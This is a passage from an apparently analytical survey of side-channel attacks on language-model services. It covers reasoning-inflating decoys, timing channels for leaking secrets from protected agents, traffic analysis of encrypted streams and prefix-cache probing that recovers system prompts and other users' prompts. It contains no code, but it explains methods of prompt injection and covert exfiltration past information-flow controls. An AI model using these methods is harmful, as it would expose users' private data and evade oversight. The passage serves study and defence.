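Many current models generate reasoning tokens, usually hidden from the user, before they answer, and they generate more for problems that take more steps. In *OverThink*, Kumar, Roh and colleagues (2025) exploited this by hiding decoy problems in documents that a model would consult to answer an unrelated question. The decoys increased the number of reasoning tokens 13-fold, 46-fold and 12-fold on three sets of questions. For one question, about the first human landing on Mars, the count rose from 384 to 10,624. Kumar and colleagues counted tokens rather than seconds, but at the 61.3 tokens per second that Zhu and colleagues estimated for Codex, the extra reasoning would take nearly three minutes.

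In a comparison on OpenAI's o1, the attack increased reasoning 14.6-fold, but every answer stayed correct and on topic, so the answers did not reveal it. The attack also worked on coding agents through poisoned files. The paper gives the largest increase for these agents as 17-fold in one place and 12.7-fold in another. The attacker must be able to query the model or a similar one while preparing the decoy, but does not need access to the model's internals.

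A sender could also choose roughly how long the delay lasts. Across three models, a Sudoku puzzle took an average of 21,080 reasoning tokens, problems from the 2024 International Mathematical Olympiad took 8,923, and a set of quantum problems took 1,464. Token counts depended less on how hard people find a problem than on how many small steps the model could check and redo.

A second method makes each token slower. Many engines use speculative decoding, in which a fast draft mechanism predicts several tokens ahead and the main model checks them together, so that predictable text comes out faster. In *Speedbumps*, Jones, Yuan and Maffeis (2026) searched for 20-token strings that make these predictions fail more often when added to a document. The strings reduced the benefit of speculative decoding by 12.2% to 36.8%, depending on the task. In the worst case, the main model needed 3.2 times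 as many passes per token. Random strings of the same length had almost no effect on two of the three tasks, so adding irrelevant text does not by itself explain the result. Since this attack increases the time per token and *OverThink* increases the number of tokens, Jones and colleagues expect that combining the two kinds of attack could multiply their effects.

Wang, Zhou and colleagues (2026), in *Adversarial Prompts for Acceptance Collapse in Speculative Decoding*, used a prompt suffix that raised the average time to answer a school mathematics problem from 26.05 to 42.29 seconds and lowered accuracy only from 82.1% to 80.2%.

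The two studies disagree about whether such an attack can stay hidden. Jones and colleagues found that most of the slowdown came from changes in what the model wrote. When they penalised those changes, accuracy largely recovered, but the attack lost 66% to 95% of its effect in all but one configuration. The placement of the suffix may explain part of the disagreement. According to Jones and colleagues, the published template for the other attack puts the suffix after the marker that opens the model's turn, whereas they kept theirs inside the document. An email's author controls only the email, so the result from Jones and colleagues is the better guide here. Both attacks also require full access to the model's weights to find the suffix, so they can't be run directly against most commercial models. Making the model reason for longer looks like a better way for a document to signal covertly.

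### The step nobody has shown

All three of these attacks slow the model down regardless of what else is in its context. To signal a secret, a document would have to slow the model down for some values of the secret and not for others.

*OverThink* hints that this is feasible. Some of its planted text asked the model to change its answer slightly depending on the result of the decoy problem, and one reasoning trace shows a model starting to comply. The model was therefore following a conditional instruction from a document while answering the user's question, although the condition concerned the attacker's own decoy problem rather than anything private. In another trace, the approach failed because the model identified the decoy as a possible attempt at manipulation.

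The threat model in *Remote Timing Attacks on Efficient Language Model Inference* (Carlini and Nasr, 2024) is the closest match to the full argument. The attacker controls part of the message sent to a language model and can observe only how long the reply takes. Carlini and Nasr compare this to blind SQL injection, in which an attacker who can't see the data in a database infers it from small differences in how the system responds to a series of crafted queries. In their example, the maker of a seemingly harmless research tool sends the crafted prompts and measures the response times. The target is an ordinary language model service without the protection of labels or a quarantined model.

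No published experiment appears to have carried out the whole chain against an agent protected by information-flow control. Each link has support only from separate experiments on very different systems: a small unprotected assistant for influence, commercial reasoning models for delay, and a shared GPU for reading hidden context from timing. An experiment that joined them would have to plant text in a document, get a quarantined model to vary its running time with a user's secret, and recover the secret from outside despite real network noise. Neither CaMeL's design nor FIDES's rules this out when the document and the secret are in the same call and the model can reason freely during it. But every link would have to work at once, and a model that usually ignores planted text would transmit the secret unreliably.

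### How much a two-second difference can carry

To estimate how much the chain could leak if it did hold, suppose that the agent sends its next request after three seconds to signal "no" and after five to signal "yes". At Codex's median speed, the two-second difference is about 120 tokens of reasoning. Suppose also that network and server delays add Gaussian noise with a standard deviation of one second. The timings and noise level are assumptions chosen to make the arithmetic easy to follow.

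The observer's best rule is to take anything above four seconds as "yes". The observer is wrong when noise pushes the delay more than one second, or one standard deviation, in the wrong direction. For a standard Gaussian variable $Z$, this happens with probability

$$p = \Pr[Z > 1] \approx 0.159 .$$

The channel capacity is the most information, in bits per use, that a noisy channel can carry reliably. For a channel that flips each bit with probability $p$, it is

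$$C = 1 + p\log_2 p + (1-p)\log_2(1-p) \approx 0.37 \text{ bit}.$$

A 128-bit key therefore needs at least $128/0.37$, or about 350, uses. An observer who keeps the exact delays, instead of rounding each one to "yes" or "no", can get about 0.49 bit per use, which lowers the minimum to about 260. Even if every model call could carry a signal, a key would take about 40 user requests with rounding, compared with 15 if the bits were noise-free.

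Those are lower limits, and reaching them requires an efficient error-correcting code, which the model would have to compute while reading an email. It would be simpler to send each bit several times and let the observer average the delays. Averaging $n$ independent measurements divides the standard deviation of the noise by $\sqrt{n}$, so the error falls quickly. The table also gives the attacker's advantage, which is the probability that the attacker answers "yes" when the true answer is yes, minus the probability that they answer "yes" when it is no. The advantage is 0 for an attacker who guesses and 1 for one who is always right.

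| Measurements averaged | Chance of error | Advantage |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 15.9% | 0.68 |
| 2 | 7.9% | 0.84 |
| 4 | 2.3% | 0.95 |
| 9 | 0.13% | 0.997 |

Repeating each bit of a 128-bit key nine times would take 1,152 uses and recover the whole key correctly about 84% of the time. Repeating each bit sixteen times would take 2,048 uses and succeed 99.6% of the time. An attacker who only wants to know whether the claim exceeds a certain amount needs about four uses.

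Real attacks are harder than this for two reasons. First, the model may not follow the planted text every time. If it complies in 89% of runs, the rate at which the assistant in *Silent Egress* leaked data, and otherwise takes the short delay, the advantage from one measurement drops from 0.68 to 0.61. Second, the noise may not be independent across measurements. A server that is busy for an hour slows every measurement in that hour, and averaging them will not remove the error.

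More noise protects some secrets better than others. If the standard deviation doubles to two seconds, the error on a single measurement rises to 30.9%, and leaking a key takes at least about 1,180 uses of the channel, or the model calls from about 134 user requests. The yes-or-no fact then takes 16 measurements to reach an error of 2.3%, fewer than the model calls in two average requests.

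## What encrypted traffic reveals about prompts and tasks

An eavesdropper can learn a good deal about a user's prompt from encrypted traffic even when nobody has tampered with the agent, and researchers have carried out complete attacks of this kind. An attacker can also plant a signal. In *SkillWatermark* (2026), the attacker publishes add-on instructions for agents ("skills") that produce recognisable traffic whenever someone uses them.

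### Why encryption leaves sizes visible

Connections to a model service normally use Transport Layer Security (TLS), the encryption behind "https" addresses. TLS hides the content of each message but not its size, direction or timing. For modern ciphers, McDonald and Bar Or (2025), in *Whisper Leak*, give the relation

$$\text{size(ciphertext)} = \text{size(plaintext)} + C,$$

where $C$ is a small constant. This is a normal property of the encryption and not a flaw in it.

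For a message sent in one piece, the formula reveals only the total length. Streaming reveals much more, because many services have sent each token in a message of its own. Suppose an agent's reply to the user begins "Your claim was denied", each word is one token, and everything else in a message takes up 100 bytes:

| Token (with its leading space) | Characters | Encrypted size |
|---|---|---|
| Your | 4 | 104 bytes |
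| claim | 6 | 106 bytes |
| was | 4 | 104 bytes |
| denied | 7 | 107 bytes |

An eavesdropper who knows the overhead can subtract it and recover the lengths 4, 6, 4 and 7. These do not uniquely identify the text, since "Your order has failed" has the same lengths. But a full reply may have hundreds of tokens, and far fewer sensible texts fit a sequence that long.

Weiss, Ayzenshteyn and colleagues (2024), in *What Was Your Prompt?*, turned this into an attack by passing the lengths to two language models they had trained to guess the text. In an account from Ben-Gurion University, their colleague Yisroel Mirsky compares the task to solving a paragraph-long *Wheel of Fortune* puzzle with no letters revealed. The task is easier because assistants write in a distinct style and repeat certain phrases. Weiss and colleagues demonstrated the attack on ChatGPT-4 and Microsoft's Copilot.

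Published accounts of the attack's success rate differ slightly. *Detecting Shadow AI* (2026) reports that the eavesdropper reconstructed 27% of responses and inferred the topic of 53%, while news coverage of the preprint in March 2024 gave 29% and 55%.

The attack is now mainly of historical interest. Cloudflare soon began adding a random-length string to each streamed token, as the researchers had proposed. According to Zhang and colleagues, major services have since adopted padding or started sending several tokens together, which largely stops attacks that reconstruct the text.

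### Recognising a topic without reading the reply

McDonald and Bar Or, both at Microsoft, tried the easier task of detecting whether a conversation is about one particular topic, in this case the legality of money laundering. They had a language model write 100 versions of the question and sent each version 100 times to each of 28 models. For comparison, they also sent each model 11,716 unrelated questions from Quora, once each. They added random spaces to make every query unique, so that cached prompts would not distort the timing. From each reply they kept only the sizes of the encrypted records and the time between them.

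They trained three kinds of classifier on these sequences. LightGBM builds a series of decision trees, each of which corrects the errors of the earlier ones. An LSTM is a neural network that processes a sequence step by step. DistilBERT is a small language model that received the sizes and gaps as invented words, with 50 possible values for each. They trained the classifiers on 80 versions of the question and tested them on the other 20, so memorising the wording would not have helped.

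The results are given as the area under the precision-recall curve (AUPRC). Precision is the share of flagged conversations that are about the topic, and recall is the share of conversations about the topic that the classifier flags. A stricter classifier usually has higher precision and lower recall. AUPRC averages precision over all levels of recall, so a score of 100% means the classifier ranked every conversation about the topic above every unrelated one. McDonald and Bar Or put the score for guessing at about 50%.

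Seventeen of the 28 models scored above 97%. (The paper's text says that 17 exceeded 98%, but its full results show 12.) A few examples show how much depended on the way each service sent its tokens:

| Model | Tokens per message | Sizes only | Timing only | Best result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Mistral Large | 1.0 | 100.0% | 64.3% | 100.0% |
| GPT-4o mini (OpenAI) | 1.0 | 98.6% | 76.7% | 98.6% |
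| Qwen2.5 Plus | 4.4 | 99.0% | 67.4% | 99.1% |
| Claude 3 Haiku | 6.0 | 80.1% | 80.0% | 91.2% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 17.7 | 78.5% | 83.4% | 84.0% |
| Amazon Nova Lite | 2.2 | 70.5% | 67.7% | 71.2% |

When each message carried one token, nearly all the leaked information came from message sizes. Gemini 2.5 Pro, which sent about 18 tokens at a time, leaked more through timing than through sizes, so grouping tokens did not remove the leak. Some of the timing signal may come from speculative decoding.

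### One false alarm in 10,000

A scanner on a real network would meet very few conversations about money laundering, so even rare false alarms could swamp the correct flags. If there are $N$ unrelated conversations for each one about the topic, and the classifier has recall $r$ and wrongly flags a share $f$ of the unrelated ones, then

$$\text{precision} = \frac{r}{r + Nf}.$$

McDonald and Bar Or projected their results to $N = 10{,}000$. For 17 models, the projected precision was 100% at 20% recall, and for eight of these it was still 100% at 50% recall. On these projections, an internet provider could find a fifth to a half of the target conversations without falsely flagging any others.

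The tests were too small to establish this. At a recall of 20%, half the flags are correct only if the false-alarm rate is as low as one in 50,000. The published projections are consistent with a test set containing about 2,340 unrelated conversations, a fifth of the 11,716. If the classifier flags none of them, the formula gives a precision of 100%. If it flags just one, the false-alarm rate $f$ is 1/2,340, and at 50% recall the precision drops to 10.5%, the figure the paper reports for four of the models.

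If no events occur in $n$ trials, the true rate could still be as high as about $3/n$, at 95% confidence. For $n = 2{,}340$, this means precision at 20% recall could be as low as 1.5%. McDonald and Bar Or repeated each test five times with different random splits, but even zero false alarms among all 11,716 questions would raise that lower limit only to about 7%. They acknowledge that they are extrapolating and advise a conservative reading.

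They also give reasons why a real attacker might do better. When they collected 121,111 conversations from one model, the attack kept improving as the training data grew. An eavesdropper could also watch the same person for weeks, and several flagged conversations from one user are much stronger evidence than one. But the comparison questions ranged from rainbows to coding courses, so the experiment doesn't show whether a classifier could distinguish a question about money laundering from one about tax evasion, which would probably produce a similar answer.

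### Padding, batching and cover traffic

A service can hide these patterns in three main ways. Padding adds meaningless bytes to each message. Token batching holds tokens back and sends several together. Cover traffic consists of dummy messages mixed in with the real ones, which McDonald and Bar Or call packet injection. They tested all three on GPT-4o mini, which was among the models that benefited least:

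| Defence | How they tested it | AUPRC before and after | Cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Random padding | On Microsoft's live Azure service | 97.5% to 92.9% | Extra bytes in every message |
| Batches of five tokens | By regrouping recorded traffic | 98.2% to 94.8% | Text arrives in clumps |
| Packet injection | By adding packets to recorded traffic | 98.1% to 93.3% | Two to three times the traffic |

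Batching seems to offer the most protection for its overhead. At Codex's median speed, a batch of five tokens goes out about every 80 milliseconds, which few readers would notice. In the simulation, batching removed most of the risk for most of the models, but not for GPT-4o mini, for reasons McDonald and Bar Or could not explain. Results from real services were less reassuring, since Qwen2.5 Plus already sent more than four tokens per message and the attack still scored 99.1% on its traffic.

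The effect of packet injection varied even more between models. Using sizes alone, the score fell from 90.0% to 72.1% for Grok 3 mini, but there was no benefit for Gemini 1.5 Flash, where the score went from 81.0% to 81.7%.

Random padding doesn't change timing, and it hides the length of a whole reply much less well than the length of a single token. Suppose each token averages 4.5 characters and gets between 0 and 32 extra bytes at random. A reply of 400 tokens then carries about 2,050 more bytes, including padding, than one of 300. The total padding on the longer reply has a standard deviation of only about 185 bytes, because variations in the padding partly cancel out. An eavesdropper can therefore easily tell the long reply from the short one, even though they can't read "denied" from one message.

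Making every packet the same size and sending packets at a fixed rate would give much stronger protection, but McDonald and Bar Or note that this uses a lot of bandwidth and delays the text. The stream would also have to continue after short replies had ended, or its duration would reveal their length. Turning streaming off, which Microsoft suggests to worried users, hides the individual tokens but still exposes the total size and the waiting time.

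Several providers changed their services after McDonald and Bar Or began notifying them in June 2025. OpenAI and xAI deployed fixes in August, Mistral in September and Microsoft in October. OpenAI and Microsoft's Azure added a field called "obfuscation", filled with random text of varying length, and Mistral added a similar one called "p". As of November 2025, some other providers had declined to make changes and several had not replied. Google, Anthropic and Alibaba already sent tokens in batches, probably to reduce the number of messages rather than for security.

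The scores for all 28 models predate these fixes, and the models are now old. Using a newer model does not stop the leak, because the leak comes mainly from how the service streams its output.

Microsoft considers that padding on Azure has reduced the attack enough that it is no longer a practical risk, but the evidence for this is thin. The attack scored 92.9% against the padded service, compared with 93.4% against the same model without padding in the main experiment, although scores from separate collections are not strictly comparable. Base rates offer stronger support for Microsoft's view, because a classifier that makes occasional mistakes is of little use for finding one conversation in 10,000.

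### Recognising an agent by its tools

Agents add pauses, tool calls and files to the stream of text. Zhang and colleagues' AgentPrint attack used these to identify which agent a person was talking to. They targeted 50 of the most popular GPTs, which are versions of ChatGPT that people have customised with instructions and tools. Knowing that someone regularly uses a GPT for medical diagnosis could reveal something private even if every message stayed secret.

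The researchers wrote 150 prompts for each of the 50 GPTs they monitored and recorded the traffic while a program typed the prompts into a browser. They divided each recording into 1,800 time slices and counted the packets and bytes sent in each direction in each slice. A neural network trained on these counts identified the GPT with an F1 score of 0.866. The score was 0.824 when the network used only the connection to ChatGPT and not the connections to other sites the browser contacted. Adding conversations with unmonitored GPTs to the test lowered the 0.866 score slightly, to 0.848.

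This was a live commercial service. Zhang and colleagues describe batching and padding as common on such services, so those defences probably do little to disguise tool use. If a GPT waits ten seconds for an outside service to draw a diagram, padding the packets before and after does not shorten the wait.

Some of the researchers' choices made the task easier. Every prompt was meant to trigger the GPT's special functions. The researchers left out GPTs that behave like ordinary ChatGPT and discarded short conversations that used no tools. They also assumed that the user talks to one agent at a time and that the eavesdropper can tell when the conversation starts. Other choices made the task harder, for example giving identical prompts to GPTs with similar purposes.

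Base rates matter here too. AgentPrint named the wrong GPT in 13.3% of cases. If these errors are spread evenly over the other 49 labels, any particular GPT gets a false match in about 0.27% of conversations with the others. Suppose that one conversation in 1,000 is with the medical GPT. The formula above then gives a precision of

$$\frac{0.867}{0.867 + 999 \times 0.0027} \approx 24\%,$$

so about three of every four people flagged would not have used it.

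Zhang and colleagues also guessed users' occupations from the GPTs they use. For simulated users in jobs where language models are most useful, the correct occupational group was among the top three guesses 73.9% of the time. For 49 real people the figure was 69.1%, but that test used survey answers about which GPTs they would use at work, not recorded traffic. The researchers added random errors to the answers to imitate AgentPrint's mistakes.

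The real-user figure is also less impressive than it looks. Of the 49 users, thirteen were managers, twelve were technologists and eight were clerks or service workers. Always guessing those three groups, without looking at any data, would have been right for 33 of the 49, or 67.3%. The simulated users provide better evidence, since the same strategy would have been right for only about 52% of them.

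### What a closed test can show

The largest public benchmark covers both ordinary conversations and groups of agents. Pouryousef and colleagues sent 60 prompts to each of ten models 100 times, which gave 60,000 interactions. They also recorded teams of two to five agents working on ten kinds of task, such as fixing bugs, analysing contracts and debating. The paper counts 2,838 team runs in most places, but its description of the method gives 3,970. Its headline accuracies are also higher than those in its detailed results:

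| What the attacker infers | Headline figure | Detailed results | Guessing |
|---|---|---|---|
| Which of 10 models | 97.7% | 95.7% | 10% |
| Which of 6 categories of prompt | 76.7% | 67.4% from replies alone | 16.7% |
| Which of 10 tasks a team is doing | up to 90.7% | 85.3% to 86.0% | 10% |

Even the lower figures are far above chance, so the traffic carries information about all three. The implications for someone using a commercial agent are much less certain.

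The researchers ran all the models themselves, although the title refers to cloud services. The ten main models had between about 3 and 15 billion parameters, which is small by current standards, and every agent team used the same 3-billion-parameter model. Their server sent each piece of text in a separate message as soon as the model produced it. Commercial services that use padding or batching would reveal less to an attacker.

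A model's fingerprint may also come partly from the serving software. The size of the smallest burst of packets in a reply barely varied between replies from the same model, but took eight different values across the ten models. Pouryousef and colleagues suggest that the way each reply ends or the metadata sent with it could explain this. If so, the service might remove part of the leak by using one message format for all its models.

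Every test was closed, meaning that the true answer was always on the attacker's list. The classifier would have to choose one of six categories, such as summarising or coding, even if a real user asked for something else. Accuracy fell only modestly when the list of models grew, from 98.5% with five models to 92.2% with twenty. Changing how the agents were organised had a much larger effect. A classifier trained on teams that worked through a central planner and tested on teams whose agents communicated directly, or the other way round, was right 52% of the time, compared with 83% when the structure stayed the same. Rewording the prompts lowered the accuracy of model identification from 93.2% to 69.5%.

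The attacker also knew where each interaction began and ended, because the researchers split the recordings at logged start and end times. On a home or office connection, an agent's traffic mixes with traffic from video calls, software updates and perhaps other agents. *Detecting Shadow AI* adds that an observer needs separately trained classifiers for each agent and provider, and that the result is only a probability and does not identify the user or program responsible.

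Li and colleagues found a weaker signal than the other benchmark suggests. They tested 13 existing traffic-analysis methods on recordings of agents at work, with network addresses removed. The best method was right 72.7% of the time when identifying which of five broad scenarios an agent was working on. Always guessing the most common scenario would have been right about a third of the time.

In the same study, accuracy was a misleading measure of how well methods detected agents carrying out cyberattacks. Only 20 of the 209 test recordings were malicious, so a program that always answered "harmless" would have scored 90.4%. All 13 methods scored above 90%, but seven caught fewer than half of the attacks, and one with an accuracy of exactly 90.4% caught only 15%. The best results came from methods originally developed to recognise websites.

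Padding would weaken these attacks but not stop them. When Pouryousef and colleagues removed all information about packet sizes and data volumes, they could still identify a team's task from the timing and order of its traffic with 54.0% to 58.7% accuracy. An eavesdropper who saw only one team member's traffic, including sizes, identified the task with 66.5% to 78.0% accuracy.

### The visits that padding leaves exposed

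All the defences so far apply to the connection between the user or agent and the model. Even if a provider disguised that connection perfectly, the insurance agent would still have to look up the address of the insurer's website and connect to it. Both the lookup and the opening of a TLS connection usually reveal the site's name.

When an agent's model runs locally, the model's output doesn't cross the network, but an eavesdropper can still observe the agent's web traffic. Jeong, Teymoorianfard and colleagues (2025), in *Network-Level Prompt and Trait Leakage in Local Research Agents*, studied agents that search the web and write reports. These agents contacted an average of about 65 to 144 different domains, depending on the agent and the kind of question. The eavesdropper sees the domain names, the order and times of the visits, and the amounts of data, but not which pages the agent read.

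To recover a prompt, the attacker first runs the same agent on their own questions and records the domains it visits for each one. They then give a language model five of these questions with their domain lists, followed by the victim's list, and ask it to infer the victim's question. If the user asked about signs of depression and how to find treatment, a guess that captures both subjects would harm them nearly as much as the exact words.

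Jeong and colleagues therefore had another language model rate how well each guess matched the original, from 0 to 1. On one set of questions, the guesses scored 0.77 for the user's goal, 0.74 for the type of source and 0.52 for the specific subject. The paper's claim to recover over 73% of the "functional and domain knowledge" in prompts is based on these figures, which are averages of a model's ratings, not the share of prompts recovered. The test used only 20 prompts. Even guesses based on 2% of the domains, or one or two sites, scored well above zero, at 0.35 for the goal.

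Including visit times did not consistently improve the results. The score for the goal was 0.73 with them and 0.77 without. The leak comes from what the agent visits, so adding random delays between visits would not help much.

A second experiment tried to profile the user. The researchers used 50 invented people, each with 32 traits, and had a language model write a week of questions for each person that reflected five chosen traits. From the domains alone, the attack could infer up to 19 traits with a similarity score above 0.7. The highest scores were for health insurance (0.98) and veteran status (0.90), but most American adults have health insurance and are not veterans, so a guess without traffic data would do well on both. Better evidence is that the scores rose by 7% to 17%, depending on the type of trait, when the attacker saw seven sessions instead of three.

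Jeong and colleagues tried two ways of hiding the visits. One was to generate cover traffic by having the agent research a decoy question alongside the real one and discard the result. A single decoy lowered the score for the user's goal from 0.77 to 0.61, and five lowered it to 0.57. Each decoy is another full run of the agent, so five decoys mean roughly six times the work.

The other defence was to visit fewer sites. Limiting an agent to a tenth of its usual domains also lowered the score to 0.61, and the quality of its reports, as rated by a language model, did not change. This gives the same protection as one decoy but reduces the agent's work instead of adding to it. Many of the sites these agents visit seem to add little to their reports while still helping an eavesdropper. The defence is less useful for tasks that depend on one revealing site. The insurance agent, for example, cannot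 get the insurer's rules from a general site such as Wikipedia.

To hide which sites an agent visits, the user has to route its traffic differently. The attack assumes that the user has no virtual private network (VPN) and that domain lookups and the start of each connection are unencrypted. A VPN would hide the sites from the local network and the internet provider, but its operator could see them instead. An agent that runs on a provider's servers, such as OpenAI's Deep Research, also keeps its visits off the user's connection, but the provider then receives the prompt, which would have stayed private with a local model. In either case, website operators can still see the visits their sites receive.

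## How shared caches and schedulers reveal other users' text

If an inference engine reuses work across customers, one customer can send a guess at another's text and learn from the response whether the guess was right, without seeing any network traffic.

### How prefix caching finds a match

vLLM divides each prompt into blocks of 16 tokens and stores KV entries block by block. It looks up each block by a key, which is a hash (a short fingerprint) of the block's tokens together with the previous block's key. Addagada (2026), in *Governing the KV Cache*, writes the chain of keys in a form that, for 16-token blocks, becomes

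$$h_0 = H(\text{tokens}_{0..15}), \qquad h_j = H(h_{j-1},\ \text{tokens}_{16j..16j+15}).$$

Each key depends on all the earlier ones, so a block matches only if the prompts are identical up to the end of that block. Suppose two users' prompts agree for 40 tokens and then differ. The engine can reuse the first two blocks, or 32 tokens, and has to compute the rest. SGLang, another popular engine, matches prefixes token by token and could reuse all 40.

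With a 7-billion-parameter model on an A100 GPU, Addagada measured a time to first token of 149.6 milliseconds when a 2,119-token prefix was new and 32.8 milliseconds when it was in the cache. Each token of skipped prefill saved about 0.055 milliseconds. A match of thousands of tokens is therefore easy to detect, but a single 16-token block saves less than a millisecond, which ordinary network delays can hide.

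Agents tend to produce long cache matches because their prompts begin with the same text on every run. Sun, Cai and colleagues (2026), in *KeyPooling*, examined 17 published prompts from the coding agents Claude Code, Cursor and OpenCode, and found that each begins with 1,559 to 8,794 tokens of fixed instructions and tool descriptions. The services they studied cached only prompts above a minimum length, such as 1,024 tokens, which an agent's prompt passes before its private part begins. An attacker can copy the public part from the software.

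### One test, then many

A membership test checks whether a particular text is in the cache. Song, Pang and colleagues (2024), in *The Early Bird Catches the Leak*, ran one on a document summariser they had built on DeepSeek's commercial service. As is common for such applications, all users' requests went through the developer's single account. The attacker prepared 200 documents of about 12,000 to 24,000 tokens, and the victim uploaded 100 of them. The attacker then uploaded all 200, once each, and took any response within two seconds as a sign that someone else had already uploaded that document. The average accuracy was 89%, with a false-positive rate of 5%. The attacker already has the document, so they learn only that somebody else is using it, but this could be valuable if, for example, the user is a law firm working on an unannounced merger.

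When the attacker uploads a document to test for it, the engine caches it, so the next upload will be fast whether or not the victim ever sent it. To repeat the test, the attacker has to get the entry out of the cache and wait for the victim to send the text again.

An attacker who can repeat the test can also recover text they don't know. If they know that a prompt begins "Imagine you are", they can try "a", "an" and "the" as the next word, keep the one that produces a cache hit, and continue from there. For a text of $L$ tokens and a vocabulary of $V$, this takes at most $V \times L$ guesses instead of $V^L$. Using a language model to predict likely next words reduces the number much further.

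Song and colleagues used this method to recover the hidden instructions (system prompts) of a chatbot running on SGLang. A single TTFT measurement detected 88% of one-token hits but also wrongly flagged 10% of misses as hits. Taking ten measurements per guess raised the detection rate to 99% and reduced the false positive rate to 0.3%. To repeat a measurement, the attacker cleared the cache with 15 irrelevant requests, then used the chatbot to make it send its system prompt again.

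The attack needed an average of 5.57 guesses and 111.46 queries to recover each token. That is 20 queries per guess, ten with the candidate and ten with a known miss, so the count seems to leave out the requests that clear the cache. For most prompts, the attack recovered only the opening. It recovered an average of 11.58 tokens from the most successful 100 of 200 prompts. The longest recovered passage was 81 tokens and took 10,260 queries. All the tests ran on a local network.

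With 16-token blocks, the attacker would have to guess a whole block before seeing a cache hit. Addagada estimates that a vocabulary of 152,000 tokens allows about $10^{83}$ possible blocks, but notes that this protection largely disappears when the attacker knows the template. If a bank's agent always sends "Show transactions for account …", an eight-digit account number leaves only $10^8$ possibilities, and checking one particular account takes a single request. This count ignores noise, and the attacker would still need to detect a time saving of less than a millisecond.

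### What each attack measures

The PromptPeek attack (Wu, Zhang and colleagues, 2025, *I Know What You Asked*) uses the order of replies instead of their timing. It relies on a scheduler that serves waiting requests with the longest cached match first. The attacker fills the queue with identical dummy requests, then adds requests that each guess the next token, then adds more dummies. Each dummy is the known text plus one very unlikely token, which the engine caches as soon as the first dummies run. A correct guess therefore matches as much cached text as the dummies and keeps its place among them, while wrong guesses match less and come back last. On one GPU, Wu and colleagues recovered all or part of users' inputs in 99% of cases when they knew the template, and 95% with no background knowledge. With one known template, they recovered a person's gender, age, weight and height in 60 requests.

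In *InputSnatch*, Zheng, Han and colleagues (2024) timed prefill and used known templates to narrow the search. On a medical question service, they recovered the exact disease in 62% of cases but the exact description of symptoms in only 13.5%, presumably because people describe symptoms in many more ways. They also attacked semantic caches, which store finished answers and reuse them for questions with a similar meaning, and recovered the gist of 43% to 100% of legal queries.

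Gu, Li and colleagues (2025), in *Auditing Prompt Caching in Language Model APIs*, tested which commercial services shared their caches. Each test compared 250 response times for prompts that should hit the cache with 250 for random prompts that should miss. They required a p-value below $10^{-8}$ to conclude that the two distributions differed, which made false detections very unlikely. In September and October 2024, they found caching at 8 of 17 providers and sharing among all customers at 7. OpenAI was one of the seven, but only for a model that turns text into numerical representations; its chat model shared entries only within an organisation. At least five providers made changes after Gu and colleagues contacted them.

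The table includes query counts from a comparison by Sun and Xiao (2026), in *Where the Savings Go*.

| Attack | What it measures | Queries | Aim |
|---|---|---|---|
| PromptPeek (Wu and colleagues) | Order in which replies return | 60 for four fields of a known template | Recover a prompt token by token |
| Early Bird (Song and colleagues) | TTFT of the guess | About 111 per recovered token | Recover system prompts |
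| InputSnatch (Zheng and colleagues) | Prefill time of the guess | 300 to 600 to learn the service's timing, then several per field | Fill in a known template |
| API audit (Gu and colleagues) | Distribution of TTFT | 250 hit and 250 miss timings per test | Find out who shares a cache |

These results are not directly comparable, because guessing a disease from a list is much easier than recovering free text. The audit best shows what was possible over the internet. Gu and colleagues tried to extract prompts token by token and failed, because they couldn't reliably detect one additional cached token and each attempt cached their own guess. PromptPeek depends on the server reordering requests, but every engine that Sun and Xiao surveyed in October 2026, including SGLang, served requests in order of arrival by default.

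### When a gateway merges its customers

Commercial services now generally confine each cache to one account, workspace or organisation. This protects customers only if they have separate accounts with the provider, and many don't. Some use gateways such as OpenRouter, which offer many providers' models through a single interface. OpenRouter gives each customer a key, but may forward all customers' requests under its own account with the provider.

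Fahey (2026), in *CacheProbe*, tested the consequences in November and December 2025. One account sent a random prompt of 4,096 tokens, and another sent a prompt with the same first 3,891 tokens. When the two accounts contacted OpenAI, Groq and Fireworks directly, there was no sign of sharing. Through OpenRouter, there was sharing at all three:

| Provider | Evidence of sharing between OpenRouter customers |
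|---|---|
| Groq | Responses reported cached tokens in 100% of tests |
| Fireworks | Mean TTFT fell from 428 to 386 milliseconds ($p \approx 4 \times 10^{-15}$) |
| OpenAI | Responses reported cached tokens in 4.8% of tests |

The Groq result required no timing measurements, because the response includes a count of cached tokens for billing. The cache sharing disappeared when customers used their own provider keys through OpenRouter, which suggests that the pooled account was the cause.

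Sun and colleagues extended the work to more models and used a careful four-request test to rule out other explanations. Alice and Bob are two customers of the same gateway, and each number is the count of cached tokens in the response:

| Request | If customers share a cache | If they do not |
|---|---|---|
| Alice sends a new text | 0 | 0 |
| Bob sends the same text | Above 0 | 0 |
| Alice sends it again | Above 0 | Above 0 |
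| Bob sends an unrelated text | 0 | 0 |

Without Alice's second request, a zero for Bob could also mean that the provider never cached the text. In the tests, accounts shared a cache for 12 of 28 models on OpenRouter, and those 12 carried 33.7% of the token volume that the study considered. None of five open-source gateways gave customers separate provider accounts by default.

On one production route, Sun and colleagues also recovered eight consecutive positions, or 16 bits in total, of a text they had planted. This shows that extraction can work on a live service if the cached-token count is precise enough, though it is far short of reading a stranger's email.

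### What the pace of tokens reveals about memory

An attacker can learn something about other users' requests even when no text matches. To produce one token for each running request, the engine has to read all those requests' KV entries from GPU memory. Wang, Fan and colleagues (2026), in *Rethinking Latency Denial-of-Service*, model the duration of a decode step as

$$T_t \approx \frac{a F_t}{BW} + b,$$

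where $F_t$ is the total number of tokens in the running requests' contexts, $a$ is the number of bytes stored per token, $BW$ is the speed at which the GPU reads memory, and $b$ covers everything else. Everyone in the batch waits for the same step, so each user's ITL reflects the memory that all of them are using together.

For the Llama-2-70B layout, $a$ is 327,680 bytes. If an agent reads 10,000 extra tokens, a GPU with 1.5 terabytes per second of memory bandwidth takes another 2.2 milliseconds per step.

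In experiments with vLLM and an 8-billion-parameter model, Wang and colleagues found a strong linear relationship between inter-token latency (ITL) and the share of the KV cache in use. They trained a classifier to estimate this share from the ITL of an ordinary customer's own requests, and its estimates followed both gradual increases and sudden drops.

A customer can therefore estimate memory allocation with only a clock and no access to the server's statistics. An agent could in principle send a signal by loading a long document into its context, which would take up a large amount of memory. The observer would see only the total, though, and on a busy engine other users' requests would constantly change it. Wang and colleagues used the estimates to time a denial-of-service attack and did not test whether a sender could transmit messages this way.

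### Reading a hit from the requests behind it

All the prefix-cache attacks so far examine the response to the guess. Sun and Xiao instead look at other requests waiting behind the guess.

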